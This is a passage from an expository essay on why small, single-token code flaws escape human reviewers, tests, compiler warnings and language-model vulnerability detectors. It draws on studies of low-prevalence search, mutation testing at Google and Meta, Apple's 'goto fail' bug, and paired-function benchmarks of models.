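People also get bored. *Low prevalence targets are primarily missed due to mind wandering* (Dewis, Hout and colleagues, 2026) analysed 60 people who each searched 1,420 displays for a T among L shapes. The T appeared in 10% of the displays for some participants and in 50% for the others. After a quarter of the displays, the program asked whether the participant had just been thinking about the search or something else.

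People missed more targets when their minds had wandered. Once the researchers accounted for this, knowing how common the targets were did little to improve their predictions of accuracy. Dewis and colleagues conclude that rarity probably also has some direct effect, although this result alone would suggest that it matters mainly because it lets attention drift. Their reasons include that the competing statistical models fitted almost equally well and that two decades of earlier research would be hard to explain without a direct effect.

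Another reason for caution is that participants in the 10% group reported more mind wandering than the others on displays that contained a T, but not clearly more on displays without one, which were 90% of what they saw. If rarity just bored people, the difference should have appeared on both. Perhaps people who have just found a T are more inclined to say that they were concentrating. If so, some of the reported wandering would be a result of missing the T, not the cause. Lapses of attention should also lower discriminability, but Caruso and colleagues found no reliable drop.

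Still, boredom probably played some part. Dewis and colleagues think they may even have underestimated its role, because asking people about mind wandering brings their attention back to the task.

### How far code reading resembles visual search

None of these studies of rare targets used code. The meta-analysis covered searches of medical images, simulated baggage, objects, shapes and letters. People doing these searches usually know what the target looks like, and can stop once they recognise it. A code reviewer who sees `<=` has to understand the surrounding program to know whether it is wrong, because the same operator is correct in most places.

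Ivory, Towse and colleagues (2026), in *Software Vulnerabilities as Cognitive Blindspots*, show that an error can be hard to find even in a short program. They gave 37 freelance programmers eight Python puzzles, none longer than 21 lines, and asked what each program would do. Six contained a security flaw, which the researchers did not mention. A flaw lowered the odds of a correct answer by 72%. Neither programming experience nor knowledge of security predicted who did well.

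The experiment was small, and only two puzzles had no flaw, so those two may have been easier for other reasons. The researchers also suspected that some participants had used a chatbot on a separate reasoning test, because 78% got full marks, compared with 17% in the study that introduced the test. But the main result fits what happened to McVoy in 2003, when he had only two lines to read and missed the equals sign.

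It also fits the first experiment by Braz and colleagues. Of the 80 participants who missed the vulnerability the first time, 60 missed it again after the warning. Rarity cannot explain those second misses, because by then the participants knew that their code contained a vulnerability. They either did not understand what the code would do or did not think of the input that would make it fail.

The rise in the criterion still seems likely to carry over to code, because it affects how people act on a suspicion, and it occurs among professionals and with very different kinds of display. A programmer who has approved hundreds of sound changes has learned, much like a baggage screener, that problems are rare, and will probably need a stronger suspicion before holding up a colleague's work.

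The shift may be smaller for code reviewers than in the laboratory, however, because they rarely learn straight away whether they were right. Caruso and colleagues warn that experiments with constant feedback may exaggerate the effect for people who work without feedback. In some sorting tasks, removing feedback even reverses the effect, so that as one kind of item becomes rare, people begin to count doubtful cases as examples of it. A code reviewer who rarely sees a real flaw might similarly begin to object to harmless oddities, although the reversal has not reliably appeared in visual search.

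There is some evidence that code reviewers stop looking too soon. In *First Come First Served*, participants were more likely to find an error if it was in the file they saw first. The difference was clear for the corner case but not statistically significant for the missing `break`. Participants did not generally believe that the file's position had mattered. This is an effect of order rather than rarity, but both effects would follow if people search less thoroughly as a review goes on. The Chromium OS reviewers' difficulty with changes spread over many directories is consistent with this, though such changes are also harder to understand.

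Mind wandering is harder to judge. Code may hold a programmer's attention better than rows of letters do. But people in the letter experiment often found the T while thinking about something else, and it is hard to imagine someone working out the consequences of a negative number in that state.

No published experiment appears to have measured the low-prevalence effect in code review by varying how often the code contains an error. In both experiments by Braz and colleagues, every participant reviewed a faulty change. The detection rates in these experiments may therefore be higher than in everyday work, where most changes are sound. They may also be lower, because people reviewing their own project know the code better and have more to lose.

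Part of the difficulty is probably that such an experiment would take a long time. A person can search a display of letters in seconds, but properly reviewing 150 lines of code takes many minutes. If 2% of the changes were faulty, each participant would have to review about 1,000 changes to see 20 faulty ones. At ten minutes per change, that would take more than four weeks of full-time work.

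## Tests, compiler warnings and deliberately altered code

A computer can run a program far more often than a person can read it. A *test* runs the program on a chosen input and compares the result with the expected one. The test can reveal a decisive change only if the correct and faulty versions behave differently on that input.

Suppose a website should admit anyone aged 18 or over. The correct condition is `age >= 18`, but a one-token change has turned it into `age > 18`. The two versions give different results only at age 18. A test at a random whole-number age from 0 to 120 has a 1 in 121 chance of revealing the error, and 20 such tests have about a 15% chance. A test at 18 is certain to reveal it if the person who wrote the test knew that 18-year-olds should be admitted. Deciding what result a test should expect is a general difficulty, usually called the oracle problem, which is also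 the term *Adversarial Test-Hardening for AI-Written Code* (2026) uses.

Programmers often judge their tests by *line coverage*, the share of a program's lines that run during testing. Coverage is a poor guide to whether tests will catch a decisive change. A single test at age 30 gives the age check full coverage but passes with either operator. A line can even count as covered when no test checks its result. *Practical Mutation Testing at Scale* (Petrović, Ivanković and colleagues, 2021) gives the example of a function that copies some data and returns the copy. The tests run every line but never check the copy, so they would still pass if somebody deleted the line that does the copying.

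### Mutation testing

Mutation testing is a more direct way to find out whether tests would catch small errors. A tool generates *mutants*, which are copies of a program with one small change each, such as a different operator or a deleted statement, and runs the tests on each copy. If at least one test fails, the mutant is "killed". If all the tests pass, the mutant has survived, and a programmer checks whether a test is missing. This evaluates tests in the same way that planting errors evaluates human reviewers.

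These are the results for four mutants of the age check when the only tests are age 10, which the program should refuse, and age 30, which it should admit.

| Mutant | At 10 | At 30 | Outcome |
|---|---|---|---|
| `age < 18` | admits | refuses | killed |
| `age <= 18` | admits | refuses | killed |
| `age == 18` | refuses | refuses | killed |
| `age > 18` | refuses | admits | survives |

The survivor shows the programmer exactly which test to add. A test at 18 kills it.

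Some mutants survive because they are not errors at all. Petrović and colleagues mention changing `size == 0` to `size <= 0` in a check for an empty list. A list cannot have fewer than zero items, so the two conditions always agree and no test can tell them apart. Such a mutant is *equivalent*: a token has changed but the behaviour has not. The *mutation score* leaves equivalent mutants out:

$$\text{mutation score} = \frac{\text{killed mutants}}{\text{all mutants} - \text{equivalent mutants}}$$

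If a tool makes 100 mutants, 10 of them equivalent to the original program, and the tests kill 72, the mutation score is 72/90, or 80%. Counting the equivalent mutants in the total would lower the score to 72%, and no set of tests could raise it above 90%.

In practice, nobody knows exactly how many equivalent mutants to subtract. *Large Language Models for Multi-Lingual Equivalent Mutant Detection* (Shu, Tian and colleagues, 2026) cites estimates that between 4% and 39% of mutants are equivalent, and no program can decide equivalence for every pair of programs. A score of 80% may therefore mean that the tests have serious gaps or almost none. The individual survivors are more informative, because a programmer can examine each one and decide whether it is equivalent.

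### Google and Facebook

Google has about 2 billion lines of code, far too many for it to calculate a mutation score. Its system makes mutants only in lines that a programmer has just changed and that at least one test runs. It makes at most one per line and skips lines nobody would want to test, such as those that write log messages. In a sample of 5,000 changes, these restrictions cut the median number of mutants per change from 820 to 7. Reviewers then see some of the surviving mutants beside the code, with links marked "Please fix" and "Not useful".

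At first, developers judged only 15% of the mutants to be useful. One unhelpful mutant changed the initial capacity of a list from 64 to 16. A test could detect this, but it would be a bad test because it would fail whenever somebody made a harmless adjustment. Google turned such complaints into more than a hundred rules for leaving out mutants, and the share judged useful rose to 89%. The true share may be lower, because the ratings come only from cases in which somebody clicked a link, about 67,000 of the 2.1 million mutants shown.

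Existing tests caught 87.5% of the 16.9 million mutants that the system generated. Most of those mutants deleted a whole statement. The 672,000 that changed a comparison, for example from `>` to `>=`, are more relevant here. The tests missed 14.7% of these, even though Google tests heavily and its tests were already running the altered lines. Some of the missed mutants were probably equivalent to the original code, though Google's rules remove the most common kinds of equivalent mutants.

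*Does mutation testing improve testing practices?* (Petrović, Ivanković and colleagues, 2021) compared files in which reviewers had seen mutants with files for which they had seen only line coverage. The more often reviewers had seen mutants in a file, the more test code programmers changed along with it (a rank correlation of 0.9, where 1 is a perfect match). New mutants in the file also became less likely to survive the tests. With line coverage alone, the amount of testing did not grow. Projects chose whether to join, so the mutant group may have contained more teams that cared about testing, but that would not easily explain why their tests kept improving.

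Killing mutants is only worthwhile if the same tests catch real errors. To check this, the team took 1,502 high-priority bugs that Google developers had recently fixed and generated every mutant its rules allowed in the affected lines. For 70% of the bugs, at least one mutant survived the tests that existed before the fix and died under the tests that came with it. A programmer who saw that mutant at the time and wrote a test to kill it would have had a good chance of exposing the bug. But the programmer might have ignored the mutant or written a narrower test, so this doesn't quite prove that mutation testing would have prevented 70% of the bugs.

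The researchers read 50 of the 459 bugs with no matching mutant. In 23 cases, no obvious kind of mutation would have helped. These included subtle changes to a program's settings and mistakes about what the program should do. Another 13 bugs needed kinds of mutation that Google doesn't use, and a fair number of those involved the wrong name, such as one variable in place of another. Swapping names is a typical decisive change, but earlier work had found that adding name mutations could easily quadruple the number of mutants.

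In *What It Would Take to Use Mutation Testing in Industry* (2020), Beller, Wong and colleagues tried to make Facebook's mutants more realistic by reversing past bug fixes, including fixes for crashes in Facebook's own apps, to learn how errors get in. Over two months their system made more than 15,000 mutants, and more than half survived the tests. Removing a `break`, the omission that about half of the participants in *First Come First Served* overlooked, produced 1,054 mutants, of which the tests caught only 31%. These survival rates are much higher than Google's, but the companies tested different code with different tests, so the comparison doesn't show that Facebook's tests were worse or its mutants better.

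The team also showed surviving mutants to 26 developers who had each recently changed the code in question. Twenty-two agreed that the mutant revealed a gap in the tests, and almost half said they would add a test or had already done so. Those who declined often had sensible reasons. For example, one developer's code was about to be retired, and another's mutant affected only a logged number. A surviving mutant shows that the tests could miss an error, but someone still has to decide whether that error would matter.

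### Mutants and tests written by language models

*Mutation-Guided LLM-based Test Generation at Meta* (Foster, Harper and colleagues, 2025) describes a system that starts from a concern such as privacy. A language model writes mutants that would cause a privacy problem and that the existing tests miss, then writes tests to catch them. Late in 2024, the system produced 571 tests. Engineers reviewed 191 and accepted 73%, but judged only 36% relevant to privacy.

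Of the 571 tests, 277 added no line coverage. They ran lines that other tests already ran, but in a way that caught an error the others missed, as a test at 18 does for the age check. A company that kept only tests that increased coverage would have discarded them.

The system also used the model to filter out equivalent mutants, but the model alone found only 47% of them. Many of those it missed differed from the original code only by a comment saying there was a bug, and the model took the comment as true. When ordinary software first removed the added comments and discarded mutants identical to the original, the combined detection rate rose to 96%, with 95% precision.

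The system keeps only tests that pass on the current code, so these tests can protect correct code from later damage but cannot expose an error that is already there. If the age check already read `age > 18`, for example, the model might well write a test that expects the program to turn away an 18-year-old.

*Just-in-Time Catching Test Generation at Meta* (Becker, Chen and colleagues, 2026) describes a newer system that looks for tests that fail. It uses the previous version of the code as a kind of trusted record. When a programmer proposes a risky change, a model infers what the change is for and how it could go wrong, makes mutants of the old version with those errors, and writes tests to detect them. If a test passes on the old version and fails on the new one, the program's behaviour has changed. The system found at least one such test for 7.9% of the changes it examined, compared with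 1.6% for an approach that wrote tests from mutants without looking at the change.

Most of these failures are false alarms, because programmers usually change a program in order to change what it does. Meta used language models and fixed rules to discard the failures least likely to be real bugs, which cut human checking by about 70%. The team then contacted 41 engineers. Eight confirmed a real bug, and four of the bugs would have caused serious failures. The precision of about 20% was tolerable because engineers needed no more than a few minutes to dismiss a false alarm. The team asked them simple questions, such as whether a condition that used to be true was meant to be false now. The system's detection rate is unknown, since nobody counted the bugs in the changes that raised no alert.

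There is also some evidence that model-made mutants resemble real bugs more closely than they used to. Wang, Deng and colleagues (2026), in *Boosting LLMs for Mutation Generation*, tested a system that looks up similar past bugs before writing a mutant. The tests that had revealed 1,991 real Java bugs also detected the new system's mutants for 92.6% of those bugs, compared with 57.9% and 32.0% for two earlier language-model systems.

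That measure is rather generous, because a mutant can fail the same test as a real bug and otherwise behave quite differently. Wang and colleagues also report a stricter one, which compares all the tests that fail:

$$\text{similarity} = \frac{\text{tests that fail on both}}{\sqrt{\text{tests that fail on the mutant} \times \text{tests that fail on the bug}}}$$

If a mutant fails 4 tests, a bug fails 9, and 2 of those tests are the same, the similarity is 2/√(4 × 9), or 0.33. The new system's mutants averaged 0.38, up from 0.26 for the better of the two earlier systems. So the typical mutant is still only loosely similar to the bug it stands for, even though most bugs have some mutant that the same tests would catch.

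### What a compiler can notice: "goto fail"

*Static analysis* means checking code without running it. Its most familiar form is the compiler warning. A compiler has to read every line anyway, so it can also flag suspicious code.

In February 2014 Apple repaired a flaw in the software that its phones and computers used for secure connections. The programmer Adam Langley explained it the next day in ImperialViolet's *Apple's SSL/TLS bug* (2014). One line appeared twice, as in this simplified version, where `step_a` and `step_b` stand for two steps of a longer check:

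```
err = step_a();
if (err != 0)
    goto fail;
    goto fail;
err = step_b();
if (err != 0)
    goto fail;
```

When a device connects to a secure website, the site presents a certificate and signs a message to prove that it holds the certificate's secret key. This function was supposed to check the signature. Each step sets `err` to 0 if it succeeds. If a step fails, the program jumps to the label `fail` at the end of the function, where the function returns `err`.

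In C, an `if` without braces controls only the next statement, so the first `goto fail` runs only after an error, but the second runs every time, despite its indentation. The program jumped to the end before checking the signature, while `err` was still 0, and reported success. An attacker could present a bank's genuine certificate without having the bank's key. Apple warned, in a notice quoted in the blog post *goto fail* (2014), that someone in the right position on the network could "capture or modify data" in protected sessions.

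Langley believed the flaw was a mistake, perhaps a slip in a text editor, but others wondered about sabotage. *Was the iOS SSL Flaw Deliberate?* (2014) cites the security researcher Steve Bellovin, who concluded that if somebody had added it on purpose, they did it fairly clumsily.

The extra line made the rest of the check unreachable, meaning that no input could cause it to run. A compiler can detect this. Langley tried a short program with the same fault in the compilers GCC and Clang, using the option `-Wall`, which leaves out many warnings despite being short for "all warnings". Neither gave a warning. Clang had a warning for unreachable code, but programmers had to switch it on separately. Langley wondered whether it raised too many false alarms to be on by default. A post on the developer site of the chip designer Arm gives this some support. Arm's own compiler warned about the "goto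 fail" pattern, but the post's author was used to seeing that warning on correct code, because programs that handle several tasks often contain loops that never end.

A narrower warning worked better. In an article for the software company Red Hat (2016), David Malcolm introduced one he had written for GCC 6, with "goto fail" as his most famous example. It looks for a line whose indentation suggests that an `if` or a loop controls it when neither does. The warning relies on the kind of redundancy that makes a loan agreement easier to check. The indentation records what the programmer probably meant, the rules of C determine what the program will do, and the compiler can compare the two.

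Even this warning caused some trouble. When GCC's developers discussed adding it to `-Wall`, one of them expected "some grief", and a message on the GCC mailing list (GCC, 2015) reported that three important software projects no longer built because of it. When somebody asked for its removal the following year, Jelinek (2016), in *Please, take '-Wmisleading-indentation' out of -Wall*, replied that there was wide agreement on keeping it and that it had found "lots of real bugs". Jelinek gave no count of bugs or false alarms, so the warning's precision is unclear. Programmers with unusual formatting can turn it off.

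Neither warning would help with the age check. The condition `age > 18` is reachable, properly indented and correct in many other programs. Static analysis can catch a decisive change that conflicts with something else in the code or matches a known bad pattern. It can't catch one that conflicts only with an unwritten rule, because the compiler has nothing to compare the code with.

A test could also have caught "goto fail" by presenting a bad signature and checking that it was rejected. Connecting to a genuine website would not have revealed the bug, because the function always reported success, which is the correct result for a genuine site. Bland (2014) argues in *Goto Fail, Heartbleed, and Unit Testing Culture* that unit tests, which check one small part of a program at a time, could have identified the bug. Langley thought a test would be difficult, because the check lies deep inside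 the process of making a connection and the tester needs separate software that can send faulty messages. Langley nevertheless set up a website that signed with the wrong key, so anyone whose browser could load the page knew that their device had the bug.

Although line coverage was little help with the age check, it would have been useful here. No matter how many tests Apple ran, a coverage report would have shown that the lines after the second `goto fail` never executed, which might have led somebody to investigate.

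### When only one rare input reveals the flaw

A tester could try all 121 possible inputs to the age check, but most programs accept far more. To be sure of finding an error that appears for just one value of a 32-bit number, a computer running a million tests a second would need about 72 minutes. For a 64-bit number, it would need more than 580,000 years. Testers therefore have to guess which inputs matter, and they usually choose typical values and obvious boundaries. The false lines in the Linux kernel in 2003 had no effect unless a program asked for an unusual pair of options, so ordinary tests would very probably have passed.

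*Beyond Rule-Based Mutation Testing* (Kiele, Saad and colleagues, 2026) measured how much a modest set of tests can miss, using two collections of short Python problems. One collection has an average of about eight tests per problem and the other about three. Extended versions have 80 and 35 times as many, respectively. The researchers counted the mutants (deliberately altered programs) that passed all the ordinary tests but failed at least one of the extended ones.

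| How the mutants were made | First collection | Second collection |
|---|---|---|
| By fixed rules | 4.4% | 5.7% |
| By language models that had not seen the tests | 12.2% | 23.0% |
| By language models that had seen the tests | 87.7% | 79.1% |

A serious project would have more than three or eight tests for code that mattered. The table also counts only mutants that the extended tests caught, so it leaves out errors that would escape those tests too. Still, the difference between the rows matters to a reviewer. Passing the tests is fairly good evidence against an accidental slip, which is made without regard to what the tests check, but much weaker evidence against a deliberate change by someone who could read the tests first. In most projects, anyone who can change the code can also read its tests, so a reviewer who is worried about intent should give more weight to tests that the author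 of the change has not seen.

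## Language models judging two nearly identical pieces of code

A language model could recognize `age > 18` as a mistake where a compiler cannot. It might infer the intended rule from a comment, or from what such websites usually do, without running the program. But the number of faulty programs a model flags does not show whether it noticed the faulty token, because a model that flags every program will flag all the faulty ones too.

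Researchers ask the model about both the flawed code and its corrected version. Most use security flaws in C and C++ programs. A typical correction adds a check, enlarges a block of memory or changes a number's type, so the two versions often differ by somewhat more than one token.

### The pair test

Ding, Fu and colleagues (2024) introduced the *pair test* and a code dataset called PrimeVul in *Vulnerability Detection with Code Language Models*. They searched the histories of open-source projects for fixes to known security flaws, and paired each faulty function with the version that replaced it. PrimeVul has 5,480 pairs, and the two versions in a pair share at least 80% of their text. The model receives one version at a time and classifies it as vulnerable or not, so each pair has four possible outcomes.

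| Faulty version | Corrected version | Outcome |
|---|---|---|
| flagged | cleared | correct |
| flagged | flagged | both flagged |
| cleared | cleared | both cleared |
| cleared | flagged | reversed |

Only the first outcome earns credit. For the list with 100 places, the model would have to flag `i <= 100` as wrong and accept `i < 100` as correct.

Ding and colleagues wanted this test because the usual scores were misleading. They trained StarCoder2, an open model, on most of PrimeVul, and it was 97.0% accurate on the part set aside for testing. Labeling every function safe would have scored 97.3%. On pairs, StarCoder2 got 2.3% right and labeled both versions safe in 88.3%. GPT-4, then one of the strongest models, tended to make the opposite error. Even when asked to reason step by step, it got 12.9% of pairs right and labeled both versions vulnerable in 54%.

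### What blind guessing would score

A score of 12.9% means little without knowing what a model could get by guessing. Suppose a model ignores the code and flags each function with probability p. Its *flag rate*, the share of all items that it flags, is then p, and the four outcomes have these probabilities:

$$\text{correct} = \text{reversed} = p(1-p), \qquad \text{both flagged} = p^2, \qquad \text{both cleared} = (1-p)^2$$

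If a model flags each version as buggy with probability 0.8, regardless of whether it is, and judges the two independently, it flags only the buggy version in 16% of pairs (0.8 × 0.2) and only the correct version in another 16%. It flags both versions in 64% of pairs and clears both in 4%.

The same model looks respectable on *F1*, a popular score that combines precision and the detection rate:

$$F_1 = \frac{2 \times \text{precision} \times \text{detection rate}}{\text{precision} + \text{detection rate}}$$

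Half of the functions in a set of pairs are faulty. A judge that flags functions at random with probability p therefore has a precision of 0.5, whatever the value of p, and a detection rate of p. This gives an F1 of 2p/(1 + 2p), which is 0.62 for p = 0.8.

| Flag rate p | Correct | Reversed | Both flagged | Both cleared | F1 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| 0.2 | 16% | 16% | 4% | 64% | 0.29 |
| 0.5 | 25% | 25% | 25% | 25% | 0.50 |
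| 0.8 | 16% | 16% | 64% | 4% | 0.62 |
| 1.0 | 0% | 0% | 100% | 0% | 0.67 |

A blind guesser can more than double its F1 by flagging more snippets, and gets its best F1 by flagging all of them. The share of correct pairs also depends on the flag rate, though less misleadingly, and a coin toss gets 25% of pairs right. Subtracting the share of reversed pairs from the share of correct ones removes this dependence, since the result is zero for a blind guesser at any flag rate.

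The rate of "correct" outcomes minus the rate of "reversed" outcomes equals the detection rate minus the false-alarm rate. A model flags the faulty version in the "correct" and "both flagged" outcomes and the corrected version in the "both flagged" and "reversed" outcomes, so the "both flagged" outcomes cancel.

### Sixty-eight models on the same test

The most detailed pair-test results come from Cichoń and Dmitruk (2026), in *A Function-Level Vulnerability Score Measures Flag Rate More Than the Model*, published in September. They tested seven models through online services on five existing sets of pairs, including PrimeVul, and one they assembled themselves. They also tested 61 open models on that last set. The open models ranged in size from 1.5 billion to 36 billion parameters, the adjustable numbers inside a model. Every model received the same instructions and judged each function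 three times, and the majority verdict counted.

The seven online models got between 6% and 25% of pairs right, depending on the model and the set. These are their results on 1,000 pairs from the researchers' own set.

| Model | Correct | Reversed | Both flagged | Both cleared | F1 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Grok 4.3 | 25% | 4% | 53% | 18% | 0.67 |
| Qwen3-8B | 21% | 11% | 44% | 24% | 0.59 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 18% | 2% | 53% | 27% | 0.63 |
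| DeepSeek R1 | 17% | 5% | 67% | 10% | 0.66 |
| GPT-5.2 | 11% | 2% | 82% | 5% | 0.67 |
| Qwen3-Coder | 10% | 3% | 41% | 45% | 0.52 |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 8% | 6% | 67% | 19% | 0.61 |

Grok 4.3 and GPT-5.2 have the same F1, but Grok got more than twice as many pairs right. GPT-5.2's F1 comes largely from flagging 88% of all the functions. Across all 42 combinations of model and set, ranking by F1 gave nearly the same order as ranking by how often the model flagged both versions (a rank correlation of 0.86). F1 had little correlation with how often the model got the pair right (0.16, within the margin of error of zero).

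For 37 of the 68 models, all of them among the 61 open models, the number of pairs judged correctly minus the number reversed was within its margin of error of zero, so the test could not distinguish them from blind guessers. On the researchers' own set, all seven online models exceeded zero by more than the margin of error, although DeepSeek V3.2 only just did. Size was a poor predictor of success. The best open models, with 27 billion parameters, matched Grok 4.3. Qwen3-8B, with 8 billion, got more pairs right than Claude Opus 4.8 but also reversed about six times as many as Opus did.

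GPT-5.2 looks slightly better when analysed with signal detection theory. It flagged 93% of the faulty versions and 84% of the corrected ones, giving a d' of about 0.5 and a criterion c of about −1.2. Claude Opus 4.8 flagged 71% and 55%, giving a d' of about 0.4 and a c of about −0.3. GPT-5.2 therefore separated the two kinds of function about as well as Opus did, and got fewer pairs right mainly because it flagged so many functions of both kinds. Correct minus reversed removes the effect of the flag rate for a blind guesser, but it still lowers the score of a model that has some skill and an extreme criterion. Both values of d' are very low. The imaginary reviewer of 10,000 software changes had a d' of 2.49, although that reviewer's sound changes were not all near-copies of faulty ones.

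Cichoń and Dmitruk also checked whether their test method had lowered the scores. They had other language models read the full answers and extract the verdicts, in case a simple search for the verdict line misread them. For the typical model, this changed the share of correct pairs by 0.1 percentage points. With 32 times as much room to reason, GPT-5.2's share rose by about 2 points on 90 pairs, which could easily be chance. They did not vary the question's wording, which is known to affect such results.

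The study is much less useful for choosing between models. On a set of 200 pairs, a 3-point difference between two models is within the noise. When the researchers ranked the seven models on each set, only 3 of the 36 gaps between adjacent models were clearly real.

### Verdicts that follow the shared text

Cichoń and Dmitruk found that 64 of the 68 models gave the same answer to both versions of a function more often than they would have if they had ignored the code and answered independently each time. Claude Opus 4.8, for example, flagged 63% of functions, so independent answers would have flagged both versions in about 40% of pairs and cleared both in about 14%. It actually flagged both in 53% and cleared both in 27%. Three of the other four models flagged nearly every function, so even independent answers would have matched almost always.

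The models were responding mostly to code that both versions contained, and Cichoń and Dmitruk conclude that this shared text determines the verdict. For example, a function that copies data from an untrusted source into a fixed-size block of memory looks dangerous, even after someone adds a length check. A model that judges by the general look of a function will flag both versions, and it will clear both versions of a function that looks harmless.

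That description fits the 37 models that could not tell correct from reversed, but it is too strong for the best ones. A model can reasonably give both versions the same verdict, since any sensible reviewer finds some functions more suspicious than others. The more important test is whether the correction ever changes the verdict, and in which direction. Among the stronger models, Opus gave the same verdict on both versions of 80% of the pairs, and when its verdicts differed, it was right about nine times in ten. Grok's verdicts differed more often and were right almost as reliably. When Qwen3-8B's verdicts differed, it was right only about two times in three.

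Opus raised a false alarm on 55% of the corrected versions, which is a problem for anyone who wants to use such a model on single functions. Ordinary sound code would probably cause fewer false alarms, but if a programmer fixed the flaw and asked the model to check the result, it would flag the function as still vulnerable more than half the time.

### A signal inside the model

A low score might mean that a model contains no information about the difference between the versions, or that the information exists but does not affect the answer. To investigate, Cichoń and Dmitruk looked at *activations*, the numbers a model computes internally as it processes text. They used a *linear probe*, a simple classifier that multiplies each activation by a weight and adds up the results. They fitted the weights on labelled pairs and tested the probe on pairs from other software projects.

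The researchers measured how often the probe scored the faulty version higher than the corrected one, a test on which guessing would be right half the time. In six open models, the probe was right for 81% or 82% of pairs. The models' written verdicts, scored the same way with ties counting as half right, scored 50% to 57%. Many of those verdicts were ties, which could have hidden a small difference in suspicion, so the researchers also compared the probabilities each model assigned to the answers "yes" and "no". This finer measure did no better than chance.

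The 82% is lower than the accuracy of a much simpler rule, which calls the shorter version faulty. Corrections usually add code, so this rule was right in 87.5% of pairs, more often than any probe. Length cannot explain all of the probe's success, because on 564 pairs whose versions differed in length by less than 5%, the typical probe still ranked 78% correctly, compared with 64% for a classifier that used only the words and symbols in the code. But on 125 pairs in which the correction had removed code, the typical probe was right only 55% of the time.

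The activations evidently contain information that correlates with the correct answer and that the written verdict does not reflect. This does not establish that the model has identified the vulnerable version, because the probe may have learned what corrections tend to look like, for instance that they often add an `if`. Such a pattern helps identify the newer version of a function but is little evidence of whether either version is safe. Cichoń and Dmitruk did not alter the activations to see whether the verdict would change, so they cannot say whether the model uses this information at all. They also did not try the probe on an untrained network, which would have shown how much of the signal came from training.

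A probe that relies on added code might be of little use when the decisive change is a single token. Replacing `<=` with `<`, for example, adds no check and leaves the length almost the same. The study has no separate result for pairs that differ in a single token.

### Functions taken out of context

Li, Xu and colleagues (2025), in *Everything You Wanted to Know About LLM-based Vulnerability Detection*, argue that tests like these understate what models can do, because a single function often does not contain enough information to judge it. Their main example is a real flaw that somebody fixed by changing the type of one number:

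```
- static unsigned short len = 0;
+ static size_t len = 0;
```

The function assembles a message from pieces and tracks the total length in `len`. An `unsigned short` cannot exceed 65,535. If the message grew longer than that, the count would restart from zero, and the program would reserve too little memory and write past the end of it. A `size_t` can hold a far larger number, so the new version is safe.

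A reader who sees only the corrected function cannot be sure it is safe. It calls `erealloc` to get more memory. The similarly named standard function, `realloc`, returns an empty result if it fails, and using that result would be a new flaw. `erealloc` stops the program instead, but a reader has to see its code to know that. GPT-4o saw only the corrected function, reasoned that `erealloc` might return an empty result, and flagged the function. The pair test would count this as a mistake, although a careful human with the same information might well have flagged it too.

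Li and colleagues gave 13 models the code surrounding each function, including the functions it called and the definitions of the types it used. On average, this was about eight times as much text as the function itself. On 400 pairs of nearly identical functions, most models were 50% to 55% accurate when given the functions alone, which is close to chance. With the extra code and a new way of scoring, DeepSeek R1 reached 67% accuracy and judged both versions correctly in 37% of pairs. It flagged both versions in only about 10% of pairs.

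These figures imply that DeepSeek R1 flagged about 47% of the faulty versions and 13% of the corrected ones, which gives a d' of about 1. In the study by Cichoń and Dmitruk, the model of the same name had a d' of about 0.4 on single functions and flagged nearly all of them, whereas here it missed about half of the flaws.

Besides the change in context, the instructions now described the type of flaw the code contained, and comments marked the lines that might be involved. Nobody reviewing ordinary work would have that much help.

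The scoring was also more forgiving of false alarms. If a model flagged a corrected function for a reason unrelated to the original flaw, the researchers told it to disregard that reason and asked again, up to four times. For faulty functions, a flag counted only if the model's explanation identified the real flaw. Both rules suit a test of whether a model can identify a particular flaw. But a programmer still has to spend time on a false alarm about something else, so the 13% rate probably underestimates how often a model would raise false alarms in actual code review.

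The explanations also suggest that models sometimes notice the correction but misjudge what it does, rather than overlooking it. Li and colleagues read cases in which DeepSeek R1 and DeepSeek V3, a related model that deliberates less, disagreed about a corrected function. In the 21 cases where R1 wrongly flagged the function, it failed to mention the correction in only 2. In the other 19, it discussed the correction and judged it inadequate, and in 6 of those it first reached the right answer and then reversed it. V3 failed to mention the correction in 6 of its 16 wrong flags. These numbers are small and come only from cases where the two models disagreed.

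Li and colleagues divided the flaws into ten broad types. The best F1 that any model achieved was lowest for incorrect comparisons, at 0.40, compared with 0.71 for incorrect calculations. This is discouraging for the smallest changes, since the one-word flaw in pyjwt is officially classed as an incorrect comparison. However, there were only 10 pairs of this type, so the 0.40 figure could be far off.

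A model may also need to know what the code is supposed to do. A written description of the intended behaviour gives the reviewer something to compare the code with. In by far the highest published result that Cichoń and Dmitruk found, a system of several AI agents first wrote down how the code should behave, and got 64% of 435 PrimeVul pairs right. The best result they found for a model without special training or extra steps was about 22%, on a different set.

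No published pair-test results appear to cover the stronger models released in the autumn of 2026. On single functions, GPT-4 got 12.9% of PrimeVul's pairs right in 2024, and the seven models of the September study got between 7% and 18%. Newer models may still have improved in ways that single-function tests cannot detect, because Li and colleagues found that larger models did clearly better when given the surrounding code, while the differences on single functions were small.

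### Pairs with wrong labels

The pair test also assumes that the version labelled faulty is faulty. Researchers usually take the label from the project's history, assuming that any function a programmer changed while fixing a security flaw contained that flaw before the change. However, programmers often also change functions that didn't contain the flaw, either to tidy up neighbouring code or to make other functions work with the correction.

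Ding and colleagues manually checked 50 functions labeled vulnerable from each of several collections. In VulnPatchPairs, one of the six sets that Cichoń and Dmitruk used, only 36% were vulnerable. PrimeVul uses two stricter rules, one of which labels a function vulnerable if it was the only one that the security fix changed. Its labels were right for 86% of the functions chosen under one rule and 92% under the other.

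A reviewer can get a wrongly labeled pair right only by making a mistake. If neither version contains a flaw, a perfect reviewer clears both and receives no credit. At the rate of wrong labels that Ding and colleagues found, such a reviewer would score only about 36% on VulnPatchPairs, so the models' 8% to 15% there is less bad than it looks. But a perfect reviewer could score close to 90% on PrimeVul, where the models did about equally badly. The smallest of the six sets has 33 hand-picked pairs, and the models got only 6% to 24% of those right. Wrong labels therefore explain at most a modest part of the failure.

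Missing context could explain more of it. Even when a label is correct, reading the function alone may not be enough to confirm it, as the `erealloc` example shows for a corrected version. Cichoń and Dmitruk acknowledge that some of their pairs cannot be decided from the function alone, and nobody measured how well human experts would do on them, so it is unclear how far the models fall short of what is possible. A corrected function may also contain a second, unknown flaw, and the test would then count a model that correctly flags it as wrong.

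### Showing both versions together

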